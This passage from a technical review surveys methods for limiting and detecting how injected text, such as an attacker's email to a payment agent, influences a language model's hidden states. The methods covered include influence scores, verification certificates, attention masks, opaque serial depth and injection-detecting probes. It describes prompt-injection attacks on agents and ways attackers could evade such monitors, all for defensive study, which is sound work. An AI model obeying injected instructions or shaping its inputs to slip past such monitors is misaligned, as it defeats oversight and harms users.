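GIF clearly did better than attention, but the simpler gradient score did almost as well, so most of the advantage comes from using gradients rather than from the part of the method that leads to the theorem. The test also requires knowing in advance which tokens belong to the attack. In a more realistic test, GIF selected one to three passages and another language model judged whether to allow the action. These judges performed about as well as judges that read the whole transcript, and sometimes better. With one passage, they used 27% to 37% as many tokens as the full-transcript judges on the two prompt-injection benchmarks.

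GIF scores from a model with 0.6 billion parameters worked almost as well as scores from the agent's own model, even when the agent's model was 200 times larger. This helps companies that rent a closed model. But the score then describes the small model's Jacobian, and the theorem does not connect it to the activations of the model that took the action.

### A bound on every layer

Sightline comes with a theorem that does limit the hidden state, at every layer and position. It relies on the fact that only attention moves information between positions in a transformer. Suppose an attention head at position $t$ gives weight $a_{ts}$ to an earlier position $s$. A change at $s$ can affect the head's output in two ways. It can change the value that $t$ receives from $s$, which the head multiplies by $a_{ts}$. It can also change the key at $s$, and with it the attention weight, but the softmax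 makes that effect proportional to $a_{ts}$ as well. If $o_t$ is the head's output and $\hat{h}_s$ is its input from position $s$, then

$$\left\lVert \frac{\partial o_t}{\partial \hat{h}_s} \right\rVert \le a_{ts}\, c_{ts}$$

where $c_{ts}$ depends on the head's weights and on its activations for the recorded prompt.

Xu and colleagues extend this to a whole model by following every route that a change can take. Let $\theta_t$ be a limit on the norm of the Jacobian of position $t$'s activations, with respect to the passage's embeddings. Before the first layer, $\theta_t$ is 1 for positions in the passage and 0 elsewhere. Each layer, with its own values of the other quantities, then replaces it with

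$$\theta_t^{\text{new}} = \theta_t\,\Lambda_t + \rho_t \sum_{s<t} \theta_s \Big(\sum_{\text{heads}} a_{ts}\, c_{ts}\Big)$$

In the first term, $\Lambda$ bounds how much the layer amplifies a change already present at the position. The second term adds the change that arrives from earlier positions, and $\rho$ bounds how much the rest of the layer amplifies that change.

Suppose there are two positions and one head per layer. The passage is at position 1, and position 2 gives it an attention weight of 0.01. If $c = 2$, $\rho = 1.5$ and $\Lambda = 1.2$ in every layer, the limit for position 2 after one layer is

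$$1.2 \times 0 + 1.5 \times 0.01 \times 2 \times 1 = 0.03$$

Position 1 has now reached 1.2, so after the second layer the limit for position 2 is

$$1.2 \times 0.03 + 0.03 \times 1.2 = 0.072$$

After $n$ layers the bound is $0.03 \times n \times 1.2^{\,n-1}$, or about 1,470 after forty. A change of size 0.001 in the passage's embedding could then move the activations at position 2 by up to about 1.5, to first order. The real movement may be much smaller, because the bound assumes that every layer amplifies the change as much as it can and that no effects cancel. With $\Lambda = 1$, the bound after forty layers would be only 1.2.

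The bound on a passage's influence at a given position is exactly zero if no chain of attention leads from the passage to that position. In ordinary attention, such a chain always exists for later positions, because the softmax gives every earlier position a positive weight. Some layers can attend only to a window of recent tokens, but information can still travel across several windows by moving to a later position in each successive layer.

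The theorem also does not cover hybrid models, which replace some attention layers with layers that carry a running summary of the text. In these layers, a token can make the model discard part of the summary, which changes later activations even if no position attends to that token.

Xu and colleagues also derive a limit on the flow that GIF measures, proportional to $\tau\theta^2$ for small $\tau$. They checked this and their other theorems in Lean, using Štorek and colleagues' Lean proof for the GIF part. The limit grows with the square of $\theta$, so a $\theta$ of 1,470 contributes a factor of about 2.2 million. Sightline does not use these numbers to decide which labels to remove. The theorem justifies looking at attention, but other results in the same paper show why a low attention weight does not rule out a passage's influence.

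### Why a score near zero does not rule out influence

Suppose a head chooses between the supplier's email and a fixed position that absorbs attention when nothing relevant is present. A number $u$ describes the email's wording, and the head gives the email an attention weight of

$$a = \frac{1}{1+e^{-20u}}$$

At $u = -1$, the weight is about two billionths. At $u = 1$, it is almost 1, and the head passes on different information, which can change the next token. A text can therefore receive almost no attention even though a different text in the same place would control the output. Xu and colleagues prove that the attention weight can be arbitrarily small in such cases.

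For each of the 11,746 true influences examined in one model, at least 11 of the model's 1,152 heads gave the relevant text an attention weight of 0.01 or more. This is good evidence about ordinary programs, but nobody had written those texts to avoid attention.

High attention to a passage does not prove that the passage has influence. A head may attend strongly to it and then multiply what it receives by zero, or another head may cancel the first head's contribution.

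Sensitivity has a similar weakness when the model is confident. Suppose the planner's score for "pay" is $20u$ and its score for "wait" is 0, where $u$ is 1 if the email confirms delivery and $-1$ if it denies it. With the confirming email, the planner is almost certain to pay, and a tiny change in $u$ barely changes the probabilities. For $\tau = 1$, the GIF score is about 0.0000006 bits. But the email alone determines the decision, and if the two versions are equally likely, the output carries almost exactly 1 bit about which one arrived.

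The score is inaccurate here even for the random changes used in GIF's own definition. With $\tau = 1$, about one change in six pushes $u$ below zero and reverses the decision, so the true flow is more than half a bit. This does not contradict Štorek and colleagues' theorem, which guarantees accuracy only as $\tau$ approaches zero.

Xu and colleagues show that the effect is general. Let $p_{\max}$ be the probability of the most likely token, and let $J_z$ be the Jacobian of the token scores. The sum of the squared singular values in GIF is at most

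$$2\,(1-p_{\max})\,\lVert J_z \rVert_F^2$$

where the last factor adds up the squares of all the entries in $J_z$. When the model is 99.9% sure of its next token, the factor in front is only 0.002. The hidden state may be just as sensitive to the email as before, because this factor comes from the softmax, which the model applies after it has computed the activations.

A successful injection may well make the planner assign high probability to paying the attacker, in which case a low GIF score would not rule out the injection's influence. In Xu and colleagues' tests, GIF had an AUC of 0.63 to 0.75 on the most confident fifth of outputs, even in a version that summed its scores over 32 tokens, compared with 0.91 to 0.96 for Sightline.

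Deleting a passage and checking whether the output changes avoids this problem, but it fails when the prompt contains the same information twice. If the supplier confirms delivery in two sentences, deleting either one leaves the other in place, so neither appears to matter. With two extra copies in the prompt, the method's AUC fell from at least 0.93 to between 0.54 and 0.69.

These results also limit what follows from an example in which Štorek and colleagues say that GIF can "certify zero flow". An agent turns a user's private notes into a public comment that includes a neighbour's name but not the home address, and GIF assigns the address a flow of zero. This correctly describes the comment, but it does not prove that a different address would have produced the same comment, and the address was still among the activations.

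### Choosing how often to miss an influence

Because a score near zero is never conclusive, Xu and colleagues use statistics to control how often Sightline misses an influence. Sightline runs the model once on the recorded prompt and output and measures how much each attention head attends to each inserted value. For one of the models, Qwen3-8B, this produces 3,456 numbers per value. A logistic regression combines them into a single score. It was trained on examples to identify which attention patterns go with a visible effect on the output. Three language models labelled the examples by reading the prompt and output.

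Sightline then needs a score threshold below which it removes a label. Suppose it has examples from 999 families of programs and the operator accepts a miss rate of 1%. It draws one true influence at random from each family, sorts the 999 scores and sets the threshold at the tenth lowest. If a new family resembles the old ones, a true influence from it is equally likely to take any of the 1,000 places in the combined ranking, so the chance that it falls below the threshold is at most 10 in 1,000, or 1%. With fewer than 99 families, this procedure cannot guarantee a 1% miss rate, so it removes no labels.

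Formally, the guarantee requires the old and new families to be exchangeable, meaning that reordering them would not change the probability of the data. It requires no assumption about the model and holds for any score, though a poor score forces the threshold so low that few labels can be removed. At a 1% miss rate, Sightline removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model. The best alternative for each model removed 22% to 38%, and GIF removed at most about 12%. When the threshold came from a different collection of programs, Sightline still removed 44% to 60%, with a miss rate of about 1%.

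The guarantee applies to the average miss rate across programs, so the rate can be higher for some outputs than for others. In a separate test where the average was 5%, Sightline missed 10% of the true influences on the most confident fifth of outputs. An operator can set a separate threshold for each level of confidence. When Xu and colleagues did this, the miss rate stayed below 1% in every fifth.

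Attackers are a more serious problem, because an email written to get a low score is unlike the texts used to set the threshold. Exchangeability then fails, and the 1% figure no longer applies. Xu and colleagues tested Sightline on AgentDojo attacks against a Qwen3-8B agent, with a target miss rate of 5%. Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels, and a policy that blocks consequential actions with untrusted labels stopped all 34 attack calls. With only 34 calls, though, the true failure rate could still be as high as about 8%. The attacks also came from an existing benchmark, whose writers had no reason to evade Sightline.

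Sightline's decision concerns only the output, even when it is correct. Sightline may correctly determine that the planner's reply did not use the supplier's email, and remove the untrusted label, while the hidden state still contains everything needed to reconstruct the email.

### Replacing one sentence with another

An attacker changes the input by choosing words, whose tokens have fixed embeddings a certain distance apart. Changing "Tuesday" to "Wednesday" moves the input from one of these points to another, while almost every small random change that GIF considers would land between tokens. A new sentence may change dozens of tokens at once. If it is longer or shorter than the old one, it also changes the number of embeddings and shifts everything after it, so the edit can no longer be written as adding a change $u$ to a single list $x$.

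The attention example shows that a local estimate can be far too small. At $u = -1$, the slope of the attention weight is about $4 \times 10^{-8}$. If the slope stayed the same, moving to $u = 1$ would change the weight by about $8 \times 10^{-8}$. The actual change is almost 1, more than ten million times larger.

The slope is so misleading because it describes a single point. Halfway between the two texts, at $u = 0$, it is 5. For two texts of the same length, a valid limit on how far the hidden state moves has to use the largest Jacobian anywhere on the line between them:

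$$\lVert h(x') - h(x) \rVert \;\le\; \lVert x' - x \rVert \cdot \max_{0 \le s \le 1} \left\lVert J\big(x + s(x'-x)\big) \right\rVert$$

In the example, the distance is 2 and the largest slope is 5, which gives a correct but loose upper bound of 10 on the change.

GIF and the routing bound both use the Jacobian at the recorded prompt $x$. The routing bound also uses the recorded prompt's attention weights, which change along the line. An operator could calculate both for every incoming email, which would help find the passages behind a suspicious payment. But however many emails the operator analyses, the results do not bound how much a different email could change the planner's hidden state. Such a bound would need constants that hold for every text the attacker could send, including texts the model attends to far more strongly than it did to the recorded email.

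## Can a transformer's hidden states be bounded for every possible input?

An attacker can choose among far more emails than anyone could test, so a bound that holds for all of them has to cover the whole set in one calculation. Researchers who verify neural networks do this by describing a set of inputs and computing a region that must contain every resulting activation. In *Conic Certification of Transformer Attention*, Ataei (2026) calls a number a certificate if some quantity in the model provably cannot exceed it for any input in the set. A correct certificate can still be useless if it is far above the true maximum.

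### Intervals and straight lines

The simplest method, interval bound propagation, replaces every number in the model with its lowest and highest possible values. If $x_1$ and $x_2$ each lie in $[-0.1, 0.1]$, their sum lies in $[-0.2, 0.2]$. The relu function, which turns negative numbers into zero, then narrows that range to $[0, 0.2]$.

The method loses precision when the same uncertain number appears twice. Suppose two neurons both compute $\mathrm{relu}(x_1+x_2)$ and a later layer subtracts one from the other. The answer is always 0, but the intervals contain no record that the two neurons share their inputs. Interval arithmetic has to allow for one being 0 while the other is 0.2, so it returns

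$$[0,\, 0.2] - [0,\, 0.2] = [-0.2,\, 0.2]$$

A transformer uses each activation in many later calculations, so these errors build up from layer to layer.

Linear relaxation keeps more of the connection. For each quantity, it stores two linear functions of the input, one never above the true value and one never below it. With $s = x_1 + x_2$, each neuron's output lies between $s/2$ and $s/2 + 0.1$. Subtracting one output from the other cancels the $s/2$ terms and shrinks the range to $[-0.1, 0.1]$, which is half as wide as before but still not zero.

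*Precise Verification of Transformers through ReLU-Catalyzed Abstraction Refinement* (2026) describes how such methods bound each nonlinear operation in a transformer and carry the bounds through to the output. It also says that verification for transformers "still remains at a very early stage". Attention is hard to bound partly because each score is the product of the current position's query and an earlier position's key, and both may depend on the email. Suppose the query and key both equal an uncertain number $u$ in $[-1, 1]$. The score is then $u^2$, which is never negative. A method that treats the query and key as varying independently has to allow for one being $1$ and the other $-1$, so it cannot rule out a score of $-1$.

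Ataei proves that finding the exact worst case for a single attention head is NP-hard when the query varies and every input number has its own interval, even with only two tokens. Because no known method solves every such problem efficiently, Ataei's certificate is approximate, but it tracks products of uncertain numbers instead of bounding one operation at a time. Halving the size of a small input set cuts the certificate's error to about a quarter, while the output's true range only halves. On the attention heads of GPT-2 small, the certificate was typically four to twenty times tighter than CROWN, a standard linear-relaxation method.

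For a single attention head, the exact worst case is easy to compute if each position can hold only tokens from a given list, which is close to what an attacker does when replacing words. But by the second layer, the activations at one position can depend on the words at many others, so a short list no longer describes them.

### How much attention can amplify a change

A Lipschitz constant is a limit on how much a function's output can change per unit of change in its input. A function $f$ has Lipschitz constant $L$ if

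$$\lVert f(x) - f(x') \rVert \le L\, \lVert x - x' \rVert \quad \text{for all } x, x'$$

A small Lipschitz constant for the map from embeddings to hidden states would limit how far the hidden states could move between any two emails of the same length. *The Lipschitz Constant of Self-Attention* (2020) proves that standard dot-product attention has no Lipschitz constant if the tokens can be arbitrary vectors.

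Three tokens, each a single number, show why. Let their values be $t$, $r$ and $-r$, and let the first token give each token $x_j$ an attention weight proportional to $e^{t x_j}$. The attention output at the first position is

$$f(t) = \frac{t e^{t^2} + r e^{tr} - r e^{-tr}}{e^{t^2} + e^{tr} + e^{-tr}}, \qquad f'(0) = \frac{1 + 2r^2}{3}$$

The slope is 1 for $r = 1$, 67 for $r = 10$ and 6,667 for $r = 100$. When the other two tokens are far apart, a slight change in $t$ moves attention from one to the other, which causes a large change in the output. Since $r$ can be arbitrarily large, the slope has no upper bound.

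Attention has a finite Lipschitz constant if the length of the token vectors is limited. According to *How Smooth Is Attention?* (2023), if no token vector is longer than some radius $R$, the constant grows at most in proportion to the square root of the number of tokens, so a context four times as long at most doubles the bound. *Lipschitz Continuity in Deep Learning* (2026), a review, confirms that attention has local Lipschitz bounds but usually no global one. Real models meet this limit on vector length because their set of possible inputs is finite and therefore bounded, as *Memory Limitations of Prompt Tuning in Transformers* (2025) points out.

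Many models also rescale their activations before each attention and feed-forward step, using an operation called layer normalisation. Zhang, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability*, use the fact that the result always lies in a fixed range. For a model of width $d$, coordinate $k$ of the normalised activations satisfies

$$|y_k - \beta_k| \le |\gamma_k| \sqrt{d-1}$$

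where $\beta_k$ and $\gamma_k$ are fixed weights. With $d = 768$ and $\gamma_k = 1$, no email can push the coordinate more than 27.7 away from $\beta_k$. Attention and the feed-forward network receive only these limited numbers, so each can add only a limited amount to the running list at a position. In a model built this way, one finite box contains the hidden state for every possible email.

A bound for every input exists, but it is very weak. The hidden state stays inside the same box whichever email arrives, but each email can put it at a different point in that box. Lipschitz constants don't give a much better bound in a deep model, because they multiply across layers. If each layer can triple a difference, twelve layers can multiply it by 531,441.

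### Certificates for GPT-2

More informative certificates cover a small set of inputs around one recorded text. Zhang and colleagues let every number in the text's embeddings vary by up to $\varepsilon$ and ask whether an attention head gives its largest weight to the same token throughout this set.

The method uses the fact that attention weights add up to 1. Suppose the weights on three tokens lie in $[0.5, 0.7]$, $[0.3, 0.5]$ and $[0.2, 0.4]$. Taken separately, the first two ranges allow a tie at 0.5. But the third weight is at least 0.2, so a tie would make the total at least 1.2. This constraint proves that the head gives the first token at least 0.2 more weight than the second.

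The largest model tested, GPT-2 medium, has 355 million parameters. The method certified the property in 41.1% of cases, while an intensive search for counterexamples found none in 90.9%. The property probably holds at a rate between these figures, so the method may miss more than half of the cases in which it holds. Each text took about 45 minutes.

The results for deeper layers are also slightly weaker than proofs, because Zhang and colleagues approximate the earlier layers by a linear function and estimate the error from samples, which can miss the worst point. They multiply this estimate by a safety factor of 1.5 or 2. They also have a strict limit on the error, but it is much looser. They found no counterexample in 450 tests, and their main first-layer results do not rely on sampling.

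The input sets are also small, which is a more basic limitation. Zhang and colleagues calculate that an $\varepsilon$ of 0.001 to 0.002 is 3% to 7% of the distance to the nearest different token. The only real text in such a set is the original, so the set does not include even the supplier's email with one word changed.

For BERT-tiny, a much smaller model, they also built sets that stretch between five paraphrases of a sentence. In the first layer, they certified one head's main target in 43% to 57% of cases and the other head's in 0% to 57%. An attacker's emails would differ from each other far more than paraphrases do.

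### Proofs that use an explanation of the model

These methods work through the arithmetic without using an explanation of how the model solves its task. In *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability* (2024), Gross and colleagues use such an explanation to shorten a proof about the model's accuracy.

Researchers trained one-layer transformers without feed-forward networks to find the largest number in a list. If a list holds four numbers from 0 to 63, a proof that runs the model on every list needs about 16.8 million runs. One possible explanation of how the model works is that its attention head looks mainly at the largest number and copies it. A proof based on this explanation could instead check how the head ranks each pair of numbers, and there are only 4,096 pairs.

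Gross and colleagues found that deeper understanding of a model led to shorter proofs, and that more faithful explanations gave tighter bounds. The main obstacle was what they call "compounding structureless errors". The weights contain small irregularities that the explanation leaves out, and a proof has to cover the worst way they could all combine. Larger models have more layers in which such errors can grow.

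*Evaluating Explanations* (2025) lists later work by Wu and colleagues and by Jaburi and colleagues that uses the same approach. It describes such a proof as giving a lower bound on accuracy over a given distribution of data. The payment assistant needs a different guarantee, because a model that is provably right on 99% of ordinary emails could still fail on every email an attacker writes, since those may all be in the remaining 1%.

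### Removing every path

A mask can give an exact result for much larger models because it removes the connection between positions instead of estimating its strength. Ordinary language models already use a mask to stop each position from attending to later ones, so if the system prompt comes before the supplier's email, the activations at the system prompt's positions are the same for every email. The positions after the email are harder to bound, and they include the one that produces the next token.

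Russinovich (2026), in *What the Model Cannot See*, blocks attention from every position outside a marked passage to every position inside it, at every layer and head. The mask sets the blocked scores to minus infinity, which the softmax turns into weights of exactly zero. Let $S$ be the positions of the passage, and let $x$ and $x'$ be any two texts with the same number of tokens. Then

$$h_t^{\ell}(x) = h_t^{\ell}(x') \quad \text{for every layer } \ell \text{ and every position } t \notin S$$

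The proof proceeds one layer at a time. Embeddings outside the passage do not depend on it. If the equation holds at one layer, it also holds at the next, because a position outside the passage receives input only from other outside positions. The two sides match to the last digit only if the server is also deterministic and unaffected by the batch.

Russinovich tested the mask on ten models with 0.5 to 120 billion parameters, the largest more than 300 times the size of GPT-2 medium. Replacing the masked passage with another of the same length changed no activation outside it. For layers that carry a running summary of the text, the server must also recompute the summary as if the passage were absent. The 120-billion-parameter model, a mixture of experts, also had to run all its experts on every token to keep the results identical.

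The passage's length and position can still affect the other activations. Padding every email to one of four lengths limits the information carried by length to at most 2 bits, and padding them all to the same length removes it. The guarantee also fails if the server reuses cached activations from a request in which the passage was visible, or if the email can contain the marker that ends the passage.

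Blocking direct attention at only some positions is not enough, because information can travel through an intermediate position. Li and Guo (2026), in *Hasse Diagrams for Attention*, represent a mask as a matrix $A$, with $A_{ij} = 1$ if information can move from position $i$ to position $j$ in one layer. Suppose position 1 holds the email, position 2 may read position 1, and position 3 may read only position 2. Using 1 for "some path exists", two layers give

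$$A = \begin{pmatrix} 1 & 1 & 0 \\ 0 & 1 & 1 \\ 0 & 0 & 1 \end{pmatrix}, \qquad A^2 = \begin{pmatrix} 1 & 1 & 1 \\ 0 & 1 & 1 \\ 0 & 0 & 1 \end{pmatrix}$$

The top-right entry is now 1, so the email can reach position 3 after two layers. Position 3 is exactly independent of the email only if this entry stays 0 through all of the model's layers.

The direction of the mask also matters. In *Can AI Keep a Secret?*, Gupta (2025) gives every token a trust level and adds a mask to Llama-3-8B without retraining it. Gupta states a theorem that less trusted tokens cannot influence the hidden states of more trusted ones. But the mask's formula stops less trusted positions from reading more trusted ones and still lets trusted positions read untrusted text, so the theorem does not follow. Gupta reports that none of 346 attack prompts succeeded and that 93.1% of output tokens matched the original model's,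 but response time rose from about 4.4 to 9.2 seconds. Russinovich also notes that tokens generated under Gupta's scheme can still read untrusted text.

### What masked models lose

For the planner, a fully masked email is much the same as one the runtime leaves out of the context, so the planner cannot use it to check a delivery. Russinovich acknowledges that deletion is simpler when possible, but a mask leaves the document intact for human readers and can hide different passages for different requests.

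*Heads of Security* (2026) takes a softer approach, using learned gates to control attention between trusted and untrusted tokens. The model can still reason about untrusted text, but that text can influence trusted tokens through any connection that remains open, so exact independence no longer holds.

Developers have also trained models with masks between documents, mainly so that a server can reuse its saved keys and values. In block attention, each document can attend only to itself, and the final block, usually the user's question, can attend to everything. If ten suppliers' emails were in separate blocks, one email could not change the activations at another's positions, but the activations in the final block would still depend on all ten.

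Adding such a mask to a model without further training lowers its accuracy, from an average of 67.9% to 48.0% in *Block-Attention for Efficient Prefilling* (2024). Training recovers part of the loss. In *Towards Generalization of Block Attention via Automatic Segmentation and Block Distillation* (2026), Li, Zhang and colleagues compared an eight-billion-parameter model with a version trained for block attention. The average score on LongBench, a collection of tasks with long texts, fell from 40.4 to 32.8. Scores on synthetic tasks fell from 65.7 to 12.2, but scores on coding rose from 24.6 to 31.3. The block version had extra training data, so the mask may not explain all of these differences. Li and colleagues report results close to those of full attention with a new training method in which the original model guides the masked one.

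### Opaque serial depth

The architecture also limits how much a model can compute before it writes something down. *Quantifying the Necessity of Chain of Thought through Opaque Serial Depth* (Brown-Cohen, Lindner and Shah, 2026) breaks a model's calculation into simple steps, such as adding or multiplying two numbers. Steps that do not need each other's results can run at the same time. Depth is the length of the longest chain of steps that must run one after another, in the shallowest circuit of reasonable size that computes the same function. Opaque serial depth counts only the steps between points that a person can interpret, such as the tokens the model writes.

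Finding the shallowest circuit is usually impractical, so Brown-Cohen and colleagues calculate upper limits from the models' known designs. For the largest Gemma 3 model, with a context of $T$ tokens, the limit is

$$11{,}322 + 20 \log_2 T$$

The logarithm appears because a computer can add $T$ numbers in pairs, then add the results in pairs, and so on. Doubling the context therefore adds only 20 steps. At the maximum context length, the limits for the four Gemma 3 models range from 4,490 to 11,662. If a model passes a running summary from token to token, the limit grows in proportion to $T$. A model that can save activations between calls has no limit of this kind.

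These numbers depend heavily on what counts as interpretable. *How Transparent is DiffusionGemma?* (2026) studies a model that revises many tokens at once over several rounds. The model's limit is 28.6 times that of the corresponding Gemma 4 model if people cannot interpret the intermediate rounds, but 1.1 times if they can. *An Operationalization of Opaque Serial Depth* (2026) considers an alternative definition that would assign the same low depth to a model that reasons in English and one that reasons in discrete symbols with no meaning in any human language.

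A limit on depth does not limit the email's influence. The model only has to look up the email's embeddings to store it in the hidden state, and a few attention steps can carry an account number to the position where the model writes the payment request. A planner could also perform all 11,662 steps without the email affecting any of them, if a mask blocked it. Depth may limit how elaborate a plan the model can work out from an attacker's text before it writes a token, but following a simple instruction to pay someone else doesn't require an elaborate plan.

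### From a box to a meaning

Suppose someone proves that, for every permitted email, coordinate 212 of the planner's last layer lies between $-0.3$ and $0.4$. The user still doesn't know whether the planner intends to obey the supplier, because someone would first have to identify which regions of the hidden-state space correspond to that intention.

Earlier researchers had identified two heads in GPT-2 small as duplicate-token heads, which attend to the earlier occurrence of a repeated name. At $\varepsilon = 0.0005$, Zhang and colleagues certified one head's main target in all 60 test sentences, but the other's in only one. These certificates are informative because researchers had already worked out what the heads do. They show how stable each head's target is, but not whether its label is right.

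A probe can provide a similar link for the hidden state. The quantities that Ataei certifies are weighted sums of a head's output, and Ataei suggests using a probe's weights for the sum. Suppose a probe with weights $c$ and offset $b$ predicts that the planner will obey the email when $c \cdot h + b$ is above 0. If $h$ lies in a box with centre $h_0$ and extends $r_i$ to either side in coordinate $i$, the highest possible score is

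$$c \cdot h_0 + b + \sum_i |c_i|\, r_i$$

Suppose the score at the centre is $-2$ and all 768 weights have size 0.1. If every $r_i$ is 0.01, the upper bound on the score is about $-1.23$, so no email in the set can make the probe predict obedience. If every $r_i$ is 0.05, the upper bound rises to 1.84 and the certificate fails, although no email may reach that score.

Even the successful certificate only bounds the probe's score. An attacker might still find an email that the planner obeys while the score stays below 0. A tighter box would not rule this out, because that requires evidence that the probe's direction tracks obedience for the attacker's emails as well as for the examples used to train the probe.

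## What do measurements of hidden states show?

A limit on a probe's score is useful only if the score tracks something that matters. Suppose a probe scores high after the planner reads the supplier's email. The high score may mean only that the email contains an injected instruction, which the runtime could also find by searching the text. It may mean that the planner represents the text as an instruction addressed to it, or that the planner is about to obey. Experiments support these three claims to very different degrees.

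### Before and after reading a document

Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues (2024), in *Get my drift?*, made an early measurement of this kind with a toolkit called TaskTracker. They gave a model a user's request and recorded the activations at the last position. They then gave it the same request followed by a document, recorded the activations again, and subtracted:

$$\Delta^{\ell} = h^{\ell}(\text{request and document}) - h^{\ell}(\text{request alone})$$

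Here $\ell$ is the layer. Both prompts also included an instruction to list the requests the model was about to carry out, so that the activations would reflect its current task. A linear probe was then trained on $\Delta^{\ell}$ to detect whether the document contained an injected task.

The probes were trained on harmless injected tasks, such as trivia questions placed in Wikipedia paragraphs. The test documents contained jailbreaks, malicious requests and coding tasks. Across six models with 3.8 to 70 billion parameters, probes on the best layer had an AUC of at least 0.99 (0.5 is chance), compared with 0.62 to 0.83 on the earliest layer.

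Such a probe might detect a change of topic instead of an instruction. To control for this, Abdelnabi and colleagues put the same question in both the poisoned and the clean documents. The poisoned version included an instruction to answer the question, while the clean version made it part of the prose with a phrase such as "you may be wondering". In the smallest model, the probe's AUC was about 0.6 in two early layers but at least 0.989 in three later ones.

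This suggests that the later layers represent a question put to the model differently from one that the text only mentions. However, every poisoned document introduced the question with the same phrase, and the probe could have detected that phrase instead. The signal fell markedly when the prompt included a warning that the text contained instructions the model should ignore, which is better evidence because the phrase alone would not easily explain the drop.

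In the same experiments, the distance the activations moved was a poor indicator of whether the model obeyed the attack. Abdelnabi and colleagues ran the attacks and had GPT-4 judge which ones worked. The activations had moved about as far in the failed attacks as in the successful ones.

### Exposure across eight models

In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States*, Dong, Liu and colleagues (2026) studied multi-step agents by running eight open-weights models, with 2 billion to 2.8 trillion parameters, on AgentDojo tasks. They applied a linear probe to the hidden state just before each response to predict whether the latest tool result contained an injection. They labelled a turn as "exposed" if it did, whether or not the attack later succeeded.

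Dong and colleagues trained the probes on eight combinations of task type, system prompt and attack wording, then tested them on 16 combinations in which all three were new. The probes' AUC ranged from 0.934 to 0.979, compared with averages of 0.46 to 0.59 for random directions. The probes' scores are slightly inflated because the researchers chose each model's best layer using the same test data.

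The new attacks also resembled the old ones more than the description suggests. One of the four test wordings is a training attack without its opening lines, and another is the same text with a list of tool calls added. Half of the test combinations therefore share most of their attack wording with the training data. Dong and colleagues found that the gap between training and test scores narrowed as they added training data, which is evidence against shortcuts that work only in the training set, but not against shortcuts that work in both. The better evidence is that a probe trained on AgentDojo had an AUC of 0.965 on two other benchmarks without retraining.

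Two of the models were also available as base models, which had not yet been trained to act as assistants. Probes on these reached 0.964 and 0.945. A base model has learned to continue text and has no particular tendency to obey a user, so these scores fit better with the probes detecting a kind of text than with their detecting an intention.

### A banner of scrambled letters

In *When AUC 0.998 Is Not Enough*, Li, Fan and Zhuang (2026) show that a nearly perfect score can be misleading. They replayed 80 recorded web-browsing tasks through Qwen2.5-VL-7B, a model that reads screenshots, and placed a malicious banner over one screenshot in each task. A linear probe on the model's activations detected the banners with an AUC of 0.998.

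They then replaced each message with scrambled letters, keeping the banner's size, position, font and colour. The same probe had an AUC of 0.489 when distinguishing malicious banners from scrambled ones. The test had only 20 banners of each kind, and Li and colleagues warn that an interval such as 0.33 to 0.65 does not rule out a moderate effect. Still, the original score is evidence that the activations record that a banner is present, but very weak evidence that they record what it means.

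Li and colleagues compared hidden-state probes for injections in a page's text or a tool's output with a classifier that did not use the activations. The classifier used four numbers, including the prompt's length and how much longer the prompt was than its clean version. It reached an AUC of 1.000, while the probes reached 0.705 and 0.771. It could identify attacks by length because each attacked prompt was a clean prompt with text added. A real monitor would have no clean version for comparison, so the classifier's higher score reflects a flaw in the test data rather than a better way to catch attacks.

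The study covers one model, and Li and colleagues call any wider conclusion a conjecture. But the control is easy to copy. For the payment assistant, it would mean comparing emails that contain an injected instruction with emails that contain a harmless sentence of the same length in the same place.

### Will the model obey?

Qin, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *BASIS*, trained separate probes for the presence of an injection and for obedience to it. Their probes use attention weights instead of the running list of numbers at a position. For each attention head, they add up how much attention the last position gives to the developer's instructions, $S_{\text{ins}}$, and to the data, $S_{\text{data}}$. Apart from a tiny constant that prevents division by zero, the feature is

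$$\rho = \frac{S_{\text{ins}}}{S_{\text{ins}} + S_{\text{data}}}$$

A head that gives 0.3 of its attention to the instructions and 0.1 to the data has $\rho = 0.75$. If an injection shifts 0.2 of that attention from the instructions to the data, $\rho$ falls to 0.25.

The presence probe had an average AUC of 1.000 across six models with up to 32 billion parameters. To train the obedience probe, Qin and colleagues ran every attack and checked whether the model followed it. They trained this probe only on attacked prompts, so it could not succeed just by detecting an attack. Its average AUC was 0.953, compared with 0.707 when they used the presence score to predict obedience.

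In one test, Qwen3-8B classified the sentiment of texts that contained injections. It resisted 322 of 500 attacks with the simplest prompt and all 500 with each of the two most protective prompts. A filter that rejected every injection would have blocked these resisted attacks unnecessarily. Qin and colleagues instead rejected an input only if both probes gave high scores. This blocked at most 12.4% of the attacks that the model would have resisted, and at most 3.8% of all attacks got past the filter and succeeded.

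This is the best evidence here that a model's internal state predicts whether it will obey. The model computes its attention weights from its activations, so the hidden state must contain any information found in the weights.

Dong and colleagues also tried to predict whether an attack would eventually succeed. For Qwen3-8B, the AUC was between 0.825 and 0.891, compared with 0.976 for detecting exposure on the hardest test. Even these lower figures may overstate how well the probe predicts success, because many of the examples without a successful attack contained no injection. A probe that detected only exposure would therefore do better than chance.

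A model can have a high exposure score and still obey the injected instruction. Dong and colleagues took 634 turns in which the probe had correctly detected an injection and had another language model judge Qwen3-8B's written reasoning and next action. In its written reasoning, Qwen3-8B never considered the risk in 31% of turns, recognised it but failed to respond safely in 47%, and recognised it and acted safely in 22%.

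Once an agent has acted, the trace may be enough to identify a successful attack. In *DriftNet*, Pinjari and Saint-Germain (2026) trained a detector that uses only logged steps and a list of the user's contacts. On synthetic data, it raised no alarm for any of the 218 attacks that the agent had resisted, and for 98.7% of the successful attacks it found exactly where the injection entered. A probe can give a warning earlier, before the model has produced a token.

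### Does the signal affect behaviour?

A probe can find a pattern that accompanies an injection even if the model never uses that pattern. Testing whether the model uses it would require changing the activations along the probe's direction, keeping the text the same, and checking whether the model becomes more or less likely to obey the injection. None of the AUC figures above comes from such a test.

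Qin and colleagues found that the presence and obedience probes relied on largely different attention heads, and they conclude that awareness of an injection and hijacking by it are "distinct internal phenomena". The probe weights show that different heads predict the two outcomes, but not that those heads cause them. Dong and colleagues say that their explanations of what the probes detect do not establish a causal role.

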